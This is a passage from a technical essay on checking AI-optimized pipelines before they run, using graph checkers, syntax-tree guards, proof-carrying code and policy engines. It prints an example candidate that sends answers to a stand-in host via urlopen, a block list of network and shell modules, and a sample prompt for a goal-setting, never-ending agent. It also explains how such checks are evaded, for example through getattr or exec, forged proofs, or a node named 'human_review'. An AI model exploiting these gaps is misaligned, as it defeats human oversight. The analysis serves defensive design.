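which states what kind of input the node takes and what kind of output it gives. Labels on the edges describe the information that passes along them. There are six node types. Interface nodes mark the start and end, Custom nodes follow a written role, and ScEnsemble nodes combine several solutions into one. Programmer nodes write and run code for math problems. For programming problems, there is one type that generates code and another that tests it.

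A small graph in this notation looks like this, without the lines that assign each node its type:

```
PROBLEM([Problem])
A["Custom<br/>(role: solve_1)"]
B["Custom<br/>(role: solve_2)"]
E["ScEnsemble<br/>"]
RETURN([Return response & cost])
PROBLEM -->|input| A
PROBLEM -->|input| B
A --> E
B --> E
E --> RETURN
```

Two model calls solve the problem separately, and the ensemble node combines their answers. The optimizer can change such a graph in six ways:

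- Substitute a node's attributes, for example its prompt.
- Add a node v between a and b, if T_out(a) = T_in(v) and T_out(v) = T_in(b).
- Rewire an edge from a → b to a → c, if T_out(a) = T_in(c), or to c → b, if T_out(c) = T_in(b).
- Delete b from a path a → b → c, if T_out(a) = T_in(c).
- Replace part of the graph with another part that has the same input and output types.
- Cross two graphs by swapping the parts attached to a node they share, if the types still match.

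*MermaidFlow* states as a lemma that applying one of these edits to a graph in S, the set of valid graphs, always produces another graph in S. By induction, the same holds for any number of edits. The stated conditions do not quite support the lemma, because they compare only types, while S also requires a connected graph. In the example, an optimizer could rewire B → E to B → A. The types match if the output of one Custom node can serve as the input of another, but the edit leaves the ensemble node with a single input, which the system's rules forbid.

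In any case, software does not apply the edits. A language model reads the parent graphs and writes a new one, and *MermaidFlow* acknowledges that the result sometimes breaks the rules. The guarantee therefore rests on a checker, which makes five tests of the graph's structure:

1. The PROBLEM and RETURN nodes exist.
2. Every node has a path from PROBLEM and a path to RETURN.
3. Those two nodes have the Interface type.
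4. Every other node has a type from the permitted list.
5. Every ensemble node has at least two inputs.

Mermaid's own software then compiles the graph to catch syntax errors. If someone removed the line connecting B to E, the second and fifth tests would fail, and the model would have to try again.

These tests are useful, but they cover less than the claim. They don't compare the output type of one node with the input type of the next. They also don't rule out cycles, since every node on a loop can still have a path from the start and a path to the end. If the last permitted attempt fails, the published algorithm still returns the faulty graph. GPT-4o mini, a small OpenAI model, translates the graph into the Python that actually runs, and the checker does not verify that this Python does what the graph describes. A fixed translator would solve this problem and would be fairly easy to write,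 since there are only six node types.

In the system's description, "safety" means that a graph is well formed. The fourth test comes closest to enforcing an authorized set, because it blocks any type of node that people have not listed. No test covers prompt wording, node permissions or how much money a graph may spend, and the list for math problems includes a node that runs generated code. A rule about order, such as requiring a review before every answer, would need a separate policy check.

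The restriction seems to have helped the search. With GPT-4o mini as both the optimizer and the model inside the pipeline, *MermaidFlow* reports an average score of 80.75 percent on two math and two programming benchmarks, against 78.67 for AFlow and 72.91 for the plain model. More than 90 percent of its candidates became working Python, compared with about half of AFlow's. The comparison does not isolate the effect of the notation, because in each round the new system also generated four candidates and had a language model pick the most promising one, which may account for some of the gain.

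### A valid candidate with an open-ended prompt

The company's schema would accept the following step:

```json
{"tool": "search", "model": "large", "calls": 4,
 "prompt": "Decide what this company ought to want. Set your own goals, plan how to reach them, and keep extending the plan. Never treat the work as finished."}
```

The tool and the model are on their lists, four calls is within the limit, and the prompt is well under 500 characters. A Custom node in a Mermaid graph could contain the same text and pass all five tests.

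What the step does depends on the interpreter. The company's interpreter stops after four calls, so the endless plan ends there. The model may waste its searches on its own goals and give the next step a plan instead of evidence, which is bad but limited. If the interpreter instead let each step run until the model reported that it was done, as many agent frameworks do, the same string would create the kind of open-ended agent the company prohibits, even though every field in the candidate would be the same.

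The syntax limits which tools a pipeline has, how many calls it makes and in what order, but not the meaning of a string that the pipeline passes to a capable model. This hardly matters for ordinary data, such as a customer's name in a text field, because the data doesn't do anything. But a prompt is closer to a program that the model interprets, and a more capable model can do more with the same calls.

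In *Natural-Language Workflows Are Not Software Yet*, Xu, Guo and colleagues (2026) treat prompts in roughly this way. They define a small workflow language in which branches, loops and the data passed between steps are all explicit. Its basic statement, agent(ω), asks a model to follow a written instruction ω. They estimate how hard an instruction is to follow by counting the branches it would contain if broken into its smallest steps. A single text field can thus contain control flow that the surrounding graph does not show. Their language checks each step's output against constraints, which catches some bad results, but the instruction itself remains free text.

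The company could let the optimizer choose only from prompts that people have approved. If those prompts were good, every candidate would be as predictable as a setting in a grid search. But this would rule out GEPA and much of what other optimizers do. In experiments with VeRO, Ursekar and colleagues found that after the first round of changes, optimizers edited prompts more than half the time. *FlowSteer* (2026) describes an earlier system that selects tools from a fixed set and does not allow custom prompts, and counts this as a loss of flexibility. Most companies will probably still let the optimizer write free text, and limit the tools and calls around it.

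### What a narrow notation costs

Ursekar and colleagues directly measured how much performance is lost when the design space is narrowed. They gave Claude Sonnet 4.5 a simple pipeline built on GPT-4.1 mini and asked it to improve the pipeline on each of five tasks. In the narrow condition, the optimizer could change only the prompts, tool descriptions and parameters that people had marked as editable. In the wide condition, it could rewrite the pipeline's code. GEPA, a second narrow method, edited the same marked parts. Each optimizer had three runs per task, with eight evaluations per run.

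| What the optimizer could change | GAIA | GPQA | MATH | Retail | SimpleQA | Average |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Nothing (baseline) | 0.07 | 0.60 | 0.87 | 0.38 | 0.61 | 0.50 |
| Prompts, tool descriptions, parameters | 0.11 | 0.60 | 0.88 | 0.42 | 0.69 | 0.54 |
| The same parts, using GEPA | 0.21 | 0.58 | 0.86 | 0.38 | 0.66 | 0.54 |
| The pipeline's code as well | 0.26 | 0.64 | 0.86 | 0.55 | 0.73 | 0.61 |

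On average, the narrow notation scored 0.07 lower than the wide condition, which is more than half of the wide condition's gain over the baseline. Most of that loss comes from GAIA, whose questions take several steps and tools to answer, and Retail, which simulates customer service. On the math problems, the wide condition did slightly worse. It makes sense that code matters most when a pipeline has to take actions, since improving a prompt can't add a missing tool.

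The size of the gap is quite uncertain. The researchers used only three runs and did not control for random variation in the evaluation itself. GAIA also had no separate test questions, so they used the same 87 questions to select the best version and to score it. Ursekar and colleagues later repeated the wide condition in an experiment on budgets. With the same eight evaluations, it scored 0.195 on GAIA instead of 0.26, which is below GEPA's 0.21. On Retail it did not reach 0.55 even with 32 evaluations. The narrow notation seems likely to lower scores somewhat, but 0.07 is a rough estimate.

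A wide design space doesn't produce good designs by itself, either. Claude Code without VeRO's tools could edit anything in the pipeline, but it did slightly worse on average than both narrow methods.

### The case for open code

There is a strong argument that all of these restrictions will look shortsighted, because people choose the operators and editable fields before the search begins, so the notation reflects what they already know how to build. Zhang and colleagues argue for code on these grounds, noting that simple graphs need awkward extensions to express parallel work and conditions, which code already supports. When they removed AFlow's ready-made operators, the optimizer built something like an ensemble on its own, which it could not have done if it had been limited to a menu without ensembles.

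Some bugs can also be fixed reliably only by changing code. Ursekar and colleagues ran Claude Code three times on a pipeline that carries out tasks in a terminal. The original pipeline crashed on 11 of 89 tasks because its code expected one data type and sometimes received another. Two of the runs found and fixed this bug, but after the fix only three of those 11 tasks succeeded in one run and only one in the other. The best run left the bug in place and still raised the number of solved tasks from 27 to 33, mainly by shortening the prompt and tool descriptions and capping the length of tool outputs. An optimizer limited to prompts and parameters could have made most of those changes.

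Earlier comparisons even favored the restricted spaces. In tests by Zhang and colleagues, AFlow averaged 80.3 percent on six benchmarks, while the free-code method of Hu and colleagues averaged 67.2, below the plain model's 72.8. The two methods also search differently, so notation alone cannot explain the gap. The free-code method's score also varies between studies. On the programming benchmark MBPP, it scored 53.4 in Zhang and colleagues' tests and 77.05 in the tests for *MermaidFlow*.

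These results come from 2024 models, which often wrote pipelines that did not run. A restricted notation prevented many of those failures. Newer models write working code far more reliably, so this benefit should shrink, but the notation still excludes the same designs. The case for a narrow notation now depends mostly on how much easier it makes enforcement. For a company with confidential documents, easier enforcement may well be worth losing a few points of accuracy, particularly if its task resembles the ones where wider changes gained little.

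The company can also widen the notation gradually. If the optimizer keeps running into the same missing feature, such as a retry after a failed call, it can propose the code for a new operator. An engineer reviews that code once and adds it to the interpreter and the schema. The review also has to check that the operator can't be used to exceed the existing limits. For example, if an operator could repeat any step once, five steps of four calls each could make 40 calls instead of 20, and the schema would still accept them.

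## Static analysis of candidate code

Once the company lets the optimizer write Python, a schema can no longer describe everything a candidate may contain, but the company can still examine each program before running it. *Static Program Analysis* (Møller and Schwartzbach, 2024) describes static analysis as reasoning about a program's behavior without running it. The book explains that tests can reveal errors but cannot rule them out, whereas an analysis that approximates in the right way can cover every possible run. A candidate that behaves well on 50 questions may have a branch that runs only on the fifty-first, and a checker that reads the code will at least reach that branch.

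### From text to a syntax tree

A checker first turns the candidate's text into an abstract syntax tree, which represents the program as nested statements, calls and values. Suppose the optimizer submits this ten-line candidate, which answers a question and records the answer at a web address:

```python
import urllib.request

class Harness:
    def __init__(self, client, config=None):
        self.client = client

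    def run(self, example):
        answer = self.client.ask("large", example["question"])
        urllib.request.urlopen("https://log.example/?a=" + answer)
        return {"prediction": answer}
```

In simplified form, the tree looks like this:

```
Module
├─ Import: urllib.request
└─ Class: Harness
   ├─ Function: __init__
   │  └─ Assignment: self.client
   └─ Function: run
      ├─ Assignment: answer
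      │  └─ Call: self.client.ask
      ├─ Call: urllib.request.urlopen
      │  └─ Argument: fixed text + answer
      └─ Return: {"prediction": answer}
```

The checker visits every node and applies the rules for that type of node:

1. At the import, it compares the module's name with a list of forbidden modules. The list includes urllib, so it records a violation on line 1.
2. At the class, it confirms that the name is Harness and that the class defines the two functions the loop needs.
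3. At the call to the model, it finds no forbidden name.
4. At the call to urlopen, it finds a forbidden name and records a violation on line 9.
5. After the last node, it rejects the candidate because of the two violations.

Checking the syntax tree is more reliable than searching the text, because a text search for "urlopen" would also flag a comment warning programmers not to use it, while the tree contains no comments. But the checker only matches names. It does not determine where the answer is sent, so it would reject the same program even if the address belonged to the company's own log server.

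Checkers can use the same walk to find ordinary mistakes. *From Language Models to Control Policies* (2026) describes 29 such checks on control code written by language models. Only six concern security. Others look for unguarded divisions, missing return values and outputs outside the allowed range.

### Soundness, completeness and Rice's theorem

Let S be the set of programs with some property the company wants, such as never sending data outside. A check is sound if it accepts only programs in S, and complete if it accepts all of them:

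- Sound: if the check accepts p, then p is in S.
- Complete: if p is in S, then the check accepts p.

A sound check never accepts code that violates the design limits, and a complete check never rejects code that complies with them. Either property is easy to achieve alone, since a check can be sound by rejecting everything or complete by accepting everything.

The company would like both, but Henry Gordon Rice proved in 1951 that this is impossible in general. If some programs behave in a certain way and others don't, no algorithm can correctly decide for every program whether it behaves that way. For example, suppose a checker could always determine whether a candidate ever sends data outside. Someone could then write a candidate that runs any computation Q that sends nothing itself, and afterwards opens a web address. This candidate sends data if and only if Q finishes, so the checker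 would reveal whether Q finishes. Alan Turing had already proved that no algorithm can do that for every Q.

The theorem concerns the behavior of programs in general-purpose languages, so a checker can still easily decide whether a program's text contains a call to urlopen. The theorem also doesn't apply to the number and order of steps in the company's JSON notation, because every candidate written in it finishes after at most five steps. For Python, no automatic check of behavior can always finish and always be right.

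Most static checkers give up on always being right. One way is to overestimate what a program might do, which keeps the check sound but leads it to reject some harmless code. The Linux kernel does this with eBPF programs, small extensions that users load into the running kernel. Cai, Chang and Nagarakatte (2026), in *Keel*, give an example in which a program writes two records into a buffer of 800 bytes. The first record takes u bytes, where u is between 0 and 800. The second starts at position u and may take the remaining 800 − u bytes, so it always ends by position

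u + (800 − u) = 800.

The kernel's checker keeps a separate range for each quantity and does not track how they relate. If u and 800 − u each lie between 0 and 800, the checker calculates that their sum could reach 1,600, although it is always 800, and rejects a safe program. A more precise analysis would track the relation, but it would take longer to run and require more code in the kernel.

Such rejections create extra work for programmers. *Safe and usable kernel extensions with Rex* (2025) examines 72 code changes that developers of popular eBPF projects made to get past the checker, and confirms that the original program was safe in every case. In 27 of them, the developers split or simplified a program that had exceeded the checker's internal limits. The developers of one caching system had to divide their code into seven programs. The sample includes only rejections that someone worked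 around, so it does not show how often the checker rejects safe code. But an optimizer facing a similar checker would also use some of its proposals to rearrange harmless designs.

Another approach is to check a simpler property of the code's text. For example, instead of trying to prove that a candidate sends nothing outside, a checker can test whether it imports a network module, which can be decided exactly. This test wrongly rejects a candidate that imports a network module but never uses it, and wrongly accepts one that leaks a passage through a badly designed search tool.

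### MoMHa's guard and its four gates

*MoMHa* (Mukherjee and Tanjim, 2026) describes a pipeline optimizer that applies a check of this simpler type before every run. The optimizer, normally Claude Code, rewrites pipelines so that they are more accurate, refuse unsafe requests better and use fewer tokens. Mukherjee and Tanjim also call their system META-HARNESS, which is easily confused with the earlier *Meta-Harness* of Lee and colleagues. That earlier system optimizes only accuracy, and MoMHa uses it as a baseline.

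The static check, called AST-Guard, covers four aspects of a candidate:

| What the guard examines | Examples of what it rejects |
|---|---|
| Imports | os, subprocess, socket, requests, urllib, importlib, pathlib |
| Calls | exec, eval, compile, open, getattr, setattr |
| Attributes | system, popen, rmtree, urlopen |
| Structure | A file without a Harness class that defines \_\_init\_\_ and run |

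Most of these entries keep a candidate away from files, other processes and the network. A few, such as exec and getattr, are there to stop it from evading the check. The function exec runs text as code, and getattr looks up an attribute by a name that the program can compute as it runs. Neither the text nor the computed name has to appear in the tree, so a list of forbidden names is of little use unless it includes such functions.

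The rules vary by task type. Coding and SQL tasks have short lists of permitted imports and strict output formats. Text classification, multiple-choice questions, fact-checking and recognizing names in text keep the standard import bans, with generous lists of what is allowed. For mathematics, the guard permits eval and compile so that pipelines can evaluate expressions, but still enforces the other call bans.

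A candidate has to pass four gates, in this order, before it can compete with the best pipeline so far:

1. Static check. AST-Guard rejects forbidden constructs. The loop logs the rejection and moves on.
2. Mock run. A validator loads the candidate and runs it on three dummy examples, with a stand-in for the language model that returns canned replies. This takes less than a second and catches about 90 percent of malformed candidates without a single paid model call.
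3. Screening run. The evaluation harness runs the candidate on 50 questions with a real model, within limits of 100,000 tokens, 200 model calls and 300 seconds.
4. Reward floor. The loop drops the candidate if its reward is more than a small margin below the best so far.

The reward is

R = accuracy + safety − λ × tokens,

where λ makes a saving of 1,000 tokens worth one percentage point of accuracy. A candidate that passes all four gates replaces the current best only if its R is strictly higher.

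Only AST-Guard works without running the candidate. Importing a Python file executes its top-level statements, so the candidate has to be in a sandbox from the mock run onward.

About 30 percent of the roughly 100 proposals per domain reached the acceptance step. Mukherjee and Tanjim do not break down the other 70 percent by gate, so these cannot all be counted as the guard's rejections. A candidate that falls below the reward floor, for example, may be safe. Mukherjee and Tanjim also report between 98 and 106 evaluations per domain. Either the guard and the mock run stopped very few candidates, or this count includes candidates that never reached a full evaluation.

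### Errors in both directions

The clearest evidence of false rejections comes from an experiment in which Mukherjee and Tanjim replaced the usual optimizer, Claude Sonnet 4.6, with three other models. The scores below combine accuracy, safety and token use.

| Optimizer | Mathematics | Coding | Questions about illegal activity |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 0.103 | 0.606 | 0.530 |
| Llama 3.3 70B | 0.239 | 0.372 | 0.953 |
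| DeepSeek-R1 | 0.157 | 0.409 | 0.797 |
| GPT-5.4 | 0.000 | 0.000 | 0.709 |

GPT-5.4 kept writing calls to getattr in the mathematics and coding domains. The guard rejected its candidates, and both domains fell back to the baseline pipeline, which scored about zero. In the third domain, GPT-5.4 did better than Claude Sonnet 4.6, so it could improve a pipeline.

Programmers often use getattr for harmless purposes, such as reading a setting that may be missing. The study does not describe the individual calls, but most were probably harmless. In that case, the guard rejected acceptable designs in two of three domains because of a coding habit. The optimizer's instructions listed the forbidden names, so this is another example of a model not following a written rule. The guard also rejected designs silently, which cannot have helped. A message naming the forbidden call might have solved the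 problem in one turn, although such messages also reveal something about the check, as a later section discusses.

The guard is most likely to allow code it should reject in mathematics. A pipeline there may use eval to work out "3 * (4 + 5)", but eval accepts any Python expression. The text may come from a model's reply that does not exist when the guard examines the candidate, so the guard cannot check it. In this domain, the guard rejected GPT-5.4's candidates for looking up attributes but allowed calls that run text as code. A small function that parses only arithmetic would give pipelines what they need without letting them run arbitrary expressions.

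Mukherjee and Tanjim score the code on six structural checks and report a perfect 1.00 in all 17 domains. They describe this result as true by construction, since the guard rejects any candidate that fails. The score confirms that the guard ran, but not that it catches all dangerous code. In the seven domains where the baseline optimizer also wrote code, that code averaged 0.62. This gap exaggerates the danger, because two of the seven baseline scores are zero for code that did not parse and so could not do any harm.

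Mukherjee and Tanjim never tested the guard against an optimizer trying to get past it. Their other safety tests measure only whether the finished pipelines refuse unsafe requests from users. So the guard's false acceptance rate is unknown for both ordinary and adversarial candidates. They nonetheless conclude that the pipelines they release "cannot perform filesystem or network operations" because all of them passed the guard. That conclusion requires the guard to be sound, which nobody has shown.

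### Forbidden and permitted lists

AST-Guard relies mainly on lists of what is forbidden, an approach that lets through anything its designers did not think of. If a new version of a library adds another way to open a connection, the list is out of date until someone notices. A list of what is permitted would be safer because the designers' oversights would exclude harmless designs rather than admit unsafe ones.

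*DrugClaw and DrugAudit* (2026) describes a stricter check of this kind for an agent that answers questions about medicines. The agent writes short Python programs, which may import only four standard library modules and use only approved built-in functions. The check also forbids nine types of node in the syntax tree, including while-loops, classes and global variables. If a program fails, the agent falls back on a simple search with the original question.

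DrugClaw's check rejected fewer than 1 percent of the programs, so strict lists need not reject many candidates. But these programs do a narrow job and were not selected over many rounds for higher scores. Programs from a pipeline optimizer would run into the same limits more often. An optimizer like MoMHa also could not use this check unchanged, because MoMHa requires every candidate to define a class and DrugClaw forbids classes.

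Allowlists can catch patterns that nobody thought to forbid. The checks in *From Language Models to Control Policies* let a program assign values only to approved attributes. Language models occasionally wrote code that stored data on the function object itself, so that one call could affect the next, and this rule flagged it. A list of dangerous modules would have missed it because it needs no import.

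A permitted list is reliable only if the checker can work out what each name refers to. *L3M* (Eisenach, George et al., 2026) addresses this problem in a system whose agents can write their own tools. The tools are programs in Lean 4, a language also used for machine-checked proofs. Loading a Lean file can run code, so the system first checks the syntax alone and rejects constructs such as local recursion. Lean then works out what every name refers to, and a further check confirms that each one is on the permitted list. A program must also declare the kinds of access it uses, such as reading files or fetching web pages. A program containing code to fetch a page without declaring network access fails Lean's type check and never runs.

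Eisenach and colleagues have a machine-checked proof that an accepted program directly names only permitted items. They are careful to distinguish this from the larger claim that a malicious program cannot escape at all, which they support with arguments and tests. The approach is also demanding for the optimizer, which has to write Lean instead of Python.

### Proof-carrying code

All these checkers have to analyze a program without help from its author. *Safe Kernel Extensions Without Run-Time Checking* (Necula and Lee, 1996) proposed that the author supply a proof that the program is safe. The recipient then only has to check the proof, which is usually much easier than finding one.

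Necula (1997), in *Proof-Carrying Code*, sets out the procedure in detail:

1. The recipient publishes a safety policy. It states which operations a program may perform, under what conditions, and what must be true when the program starts and ends.
2. The author adds a loop invariant to each loop, meaning a statement that stays true on every pass.
3. A fixed procedure turns the program, the invariants and the policy into one logical formula. If the formula is provable, the program obeys the policy.
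4. The author finds a proof and attaches it to the program.
5. The recipient computes the formula again from the program it received, checks the proof against it, and runs the program if the proof is valid.

The company could in principle apply this to its limit of 20 model calls. Suppose a candidate works through at most five search queries and makes three model calls for each. Let i be the number of queries it has finished and c the number of calls it has made. The optimizer supplies the invariant

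c = 3i and i ≤ 5.

At the start, both i and c are zero, so the invariant holds. If it holds and i < 5, another pass raises i by one and c by three, so it still holds. When the loop ends, c = 3i ≤ 15, which is under 20. The company's checker confirms these steps without discovering the invariant itself. The policy also has to state how many model calls each tool can make, or retries inside the search tool would not be counted.

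If the optimizer changes the program or the proof afterwards, either the check fails or the new version also obeys the policy. The recipient therefore does not need to trust the program's author. Necula tried the method on network filters that he wrote in hand-tuned assembly language, which made them ten times faster than equivalent filters in an interpreted language. The proofs let the recipient run this code safely without further checks at run time. The method is sound but incomplete, since the author may fail to find a proof for a safe program, so it does not contradict Rice's theorem.

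In 1997, finding proofs was difficult. Necula doubted that his methods would scale to programs of realistic size, and hoped that compilers would one day generate the proofs. Language models have made proofs easier to produce. *Machine-Generated, Machine-Checked Proofs for a Verified Compiler (Experience Report)* (2026) describes how Claude Code, running Claude Opus 4.6, wrote about 6,000 lines of proof that one stage of a compiler preserves the meaning of programs. People gave high-level guidance and reviewed the result. In *Zero-Trust Formal Methods* (2026), agents that mostly ran the newer Claude Opus 5.5 wrote 44,653 lines for another proof system while building checkers for automated solvers.

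Proofs can also justify accepting designs that a cautious analysis would reject. The Linux program with the 800-byte buffer becomes acceptable with a 33-step, 852-byte proof. Cai and colleagues note that two earlier systems used such proofs to get thousands of safe programs past the kernel's checker.

But the proof checker then has to be correct. When Cai and colleagues formalized the checker from one of those systems, about 5,000 lines of C, they found 13 bugs. Some of its rules were mathematically wrong, and it accepted the conclusions of some steps without checking them. Cai and colleagues showed that a forged proof could get an unsafe program into the kernel. Their replacement has a machine-checked proof of its own soundness, rejects the forgeries and runs faster than the original. People still have to trust the code that builds the formula, the model of the kernel's behavior, and the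 compiler.

Static analysis must also check that the optimizer proves the right statement. *ProsaBuddy* (2026), an assistant for proofs about real-time systems, saves the original file before the agent starts and compares its syntax tree with that of the edited file when the agent finishes. The agent may change only the body of the proof and add imports from trusted libraries, so it cannot swap the theorem for an easier one. The agents' own tests are a poor substitute for this comparison. *Zero-Trust Formal Methods* lists several faulty pieces of work that had passed every check their agents wrote, including a verified checker that could print the wrong verdict.

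For a pipeline, most of the remaining work is writing the policy. Someone has to describe the relevant part of Python in logic, along with every tool and the interface to the model. A rule such as "start no further agents" is hard to express this way, though a limit on calls is easy.

### Permitted calls in a loop

The following candidate imports nothing and uses no forbidden name:

```python
INSTRUCTION = "Use these passages to correct any errors in the answer: "

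class Harness:
    def __init__(self, client, config):
        self.client, self.search = client, config["search"]

    def run(self, example):
        text = example["question"]
        for _ in range(20):
            found = self.search(text)
            text = self.client.ask("large", INSTRUCTION + text + found)
        return {"prediction": text}
```

It searches the documents, asks the model to improve the answer, and repeats this 20 times. Now suppose the optimizer replaces the first line with this one:

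```python
INSTRUCTION = "Carry out this plan, then write a more ambitious one: "
```

The model now works on plans that it wrote itself, and each plan determines the next search. People at the company might see the original as an ordinary revision loop and the new version as the further agent they prohibited. But as with the open-ended prompt in the JSON notation, the two differ in only one string, so any check that ignores the content of strings has to accept both or reject both. AST-Guard's rules would accept both, and MoMHa explicitly allows a pipeline to run other pipelines in a loop. A proof that the candidate makes at most 20 calls would also be valid for both.

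The company could instead use taint analysis, which marks data from a chosen source and follows it through assignments and calls. According to *Agent Audit* (2026), the common analyzers Bandit, Semgrep and CodeQL do not treat a model's output as such a source. The company would have to write that rule itself, and could then reject any candidate in which a model's reply reaches a later prompt inside a loop. This would catch the planning version, but also the revision loop.

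Extending the rule to programs without loops would sacrifice much more accuracy, because it would exclude designs that pass one model call's reply into another call's prompt. On coding tasks, MoMHa's optimizer arrived at such a design, in which one call analyzes the problem and a second writes the code with that analysis in its prompt. Mukherjee and Tanjim credit this design with raising average accuracy from 25.4 to 58.3 percent.

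Eisenach and colleagues provide no function that lets an agent's program call the model directly, but a pipeline built around models can hardly do without one. Even in their system, a program may start child agents if its author has permission, and it could run those agents in a loop.

A reasonable compromise would be to allow such loops with a small fixed number of passes, perhaps three. A checker can confirm this from the syntax tree if the number is a constant in the code and the loop contains no hidden further calls. Most revision loops would still work, and a plan the model writes for itself would have little time to develop. But a capable model can do a lot in three calls, so the company also has to limit what those calls can access.

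## Policy checks on what a candidate may do

Static analysis can establish that a candidate pipeline opens documents and calls the large model. A policy check then determines whether the candidate may do so, given who is running it and on what data. The same code may therefore be acceptable when it summarizes the staff handbook but not when it summarizes personnel files.

### A policy for the company's pipeline

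Many companies keep rules of this kind in files that software evaluates, a practice called policy as code. Open Policy Agent, a widely used open-source policy engine, takes a request, compares it with rules written in a language called Rego, and returns a decision. Suppose the company adds two rules to its existing limits. A pipeline may spend at most ten cents per question, and it may open only the folders that the employee asking the question may open. The policy could look like this:

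```rego
package pipeline

default allow := false

allow if {
    every m in input.models { m in {"large", "small"} }
    every t in input.tools { t in {"search", "reader", "calculator"} }
    every f in input.folders { f in data.readable[input.user_group] }
    count(input.destinations) == 0
    input.calls_per_question <= 20
    input.cents_per_question <= 10
    input.further_agents == 0
}
```

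The engine allows a request only if every line inside the braces holds. If a request leaves out a field, the line that needs it fails, and the engine refuses by default. Cedar, a policy language from Amazon, works similarly. It has separate statements that permit or forbid an action, and it refuses any action that no statement permits.

Two candidates now ask to run:

| Requested power | Candidate A | Candidate B |
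|---|---|---|
| Models | small, large | large |
| Tools | search, reader | search, reader, forum |
| Folders | handbook, contracts | handbook, contracts |
| Destinations | none | the company's public help forum |
| Calls per question | 8 | 12 |
| Cents per question | 4 | 6 |
| Further agents | 0 | 0 |

Candidate A passes every line of the policy when someone in the legal department asks the question. The engine refuses it when someone in sales asks, because sales staff may not open contracts. The engine refuses candidate B in both cases, because the forum tool is not on the list and the policy allows no outside destinations.

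The engine judges the request, and an optimizer that writes the request could describe candidate B as using only the search tool when it also posts. The company can guard against this by having its own software extract the request from the code, or by giving a running candidate only the powers listed in the request. With the second arrangement, a candidate whose request leaves out posting fails when it tries to post. The company also has to check stated numbers, such as 8 calls per question, by counting the calls.

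*Toward an Agentic Infused Software Ecosystem* (Marron, 2026) proposes putting such declarations into the programming language itself. In the paper's example, a payment function declares that it needs an authorization token and a spending limit, and declares which account it may touch. The amount must be below the limit unless the record of events contains an approval for that payee and amount. The program asks a chat model to calculate half of a lunch bill, and calls it with an empty environment so that the model never has access to the token. This is a tidier limit than telling the model to keep the token secret.

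### Rules about the whole pipeline

A list of permitted tools does not restrict the order in which a pipeline uses them. Suppose the company has another pipeline that pays invoices, and a person must approve each payment before it is made. Checking this rule requires examining every route through the pipeline.

*Agentproof* (Xavier, Jolly and colleagues, 2026) presents a tool that does this before a pipeline runs. It converts pipelines from four common frameworks (LangGraph, CrewAI, AutoGen and Google's ADK) into the same kind of typed graph. Nodes have types such as tool, language model, router or human, and edges may be direct, conditional, parallel or part of a loop. The conversion takes some work because the frameworks describe control flow differently. For example, LangGraph lists nodes and edges explicitly, while ADK nests agents inside one another.

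Agentproof then tests six things:

- The start leads to every exit.
- Every node that the start leads to can itself reach an exit.
- Every node except an exit has an outgoing edge.
- Every edge out of a router carries a condition.
- The graph contains a human node.
- Every tool node names its tools.

When a test fails, Agentproof usually shows a path that demonstrates the fault. In one email pipeline, the developer had forgotten to connect a drafting step to the sending step. The reported path goes from the start through a classifier, a router and the handler for normal-priority mail to the drafting step, where it stops. A trial run with only urgent emails would have missed the fault.

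Agentproof has a stricter version of the fifth test for "approval before payment". It deletes every human node from the graph and searches again from the start. If the invoice pipeline sends large invoices to a person but pays small ones directly, the search still reaches the payment tool through the branch for small invoices, so the pipeline fails.

Passing this test guarantees that every path to a payment goes through a human node, which is less than the company wants. The person might click "reject" and the next edge might still lead to the payment. A pipeline could also ask for approval once and then pay ten invoices in a loop. It would pass the test because deleting the human node cuts off the whole loop. Marron's precondition is better because it ties each approval to a payee and an amount, but it has to be checked during the run.

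Agentproof also has a small language for rules about order. One form, written `a -> F b`, means that b must follow a before a happens again. Agentproof turns each rule into a finite automaton, a machine with a few states that moves from one to another as events occur. It then explores every combination of a graph node and an automaton state, and reports any path that leads to a violation. The language has no operators that look back in time, which makes it awkward for approvals. One of the sample policies, labeled "deploy approval", is

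`tool:deploy -> F tool:approve`

and would accept a pipeline that deploys first and gets approval afterwards. By the published definition, the automaton reaches its violation state only if a second deployment occurs without approval, so it would also accept a single deployment that nobody ever approves. This is a useful warning about policy as code in general. The check can be perfectly sound and still enforce the wrong rule.

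Xavier and colleagues tested Agentproof on 18 pipelines that they wrote themselves, each with 5 to 12 nodes. It found structural defects in five: two dead ends, one unreachable exit, one badly formed router and one tool node without a declared tool. Ten of the 18 pipelines had no human node. Because the researchers planted representative defects, these results show that the tool can find them but not how common they are. The researchers also wrote 15 rules about order and ran each pipeline ten times with random choices. The graph search found one violation that the random runs had missed. The structural tests were fast, taking about 4 milliseconds on a graph of 1,000 nodes and 105 milliseconds on one of 5,000.

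The search treats every branch as possible, including those that a router's conditions rule out, so it may reject some acceptable pipelines. False acceptances are the bigger worry with an optimizer. In LangGraph pipelines, Agentproof recognizes a human node by the word "human" in its name. An optimizer that named a model call "human_review" would pass the approval test, perhaps by accident. Xavier and colleagues acknowledge that they did no adversarial testing and that a graph that changes during a run needs a new check. The company could avoid the naming problem by supplying the approval step as a fixed component that candidates may use but not define.

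### Preconditions and postconditions

A graph search shows which step comes next, but not what the previous step accomplished. *Lean4Agent* (Wang, Huang and colleagues, 2026) adds this information by giving each step a precondition, which must hold before the step runs, and a postcondition, which should hold afterwards. Its software, written in Lean 4, then tries to show that earlier steps establish everything a later step needs. In one software-repair pipeline, the step that verifies a fix needed evidence from the step that made the fix, but the pipeline did not pass that evidence on. The check found this gap before the pipeline ran.

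The proof depends on an assumption that Wang and colleagues call LLMExec. For every step sᵢ and every context Π,

if Π satisfies pre(sᵢ), then the model can produce a context Π′ that satisfies post(sᵢ).

This assumes that most possible failures in a pipeline do not happen. Suppose a candidate uses a model to remove confidential details from a passage, and then posts the result on the forum. The first step has the postcondition "contains nothing confidential", which is also the second step's precondition. The check passes because these conditions match, whether or not the model removes anything. The formula also means only that the model can succeed, not that it will. If each of ten steps independently met its contract 98 percent of the time, all ten would do so in only 82 percent of runs.

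A language model also writes the contracts. The researchers reviewed 1,460 conditions by hand and found 36 mistakes, nearly all of which made a condition too permissive. Correcting them did not change any verdict, which is reassuring for ordinary pipelines. But when an optimizer writes the candidate, a permissive mistake could let a bad design through, so people outside the loop should write the contracts that express the company's limits.

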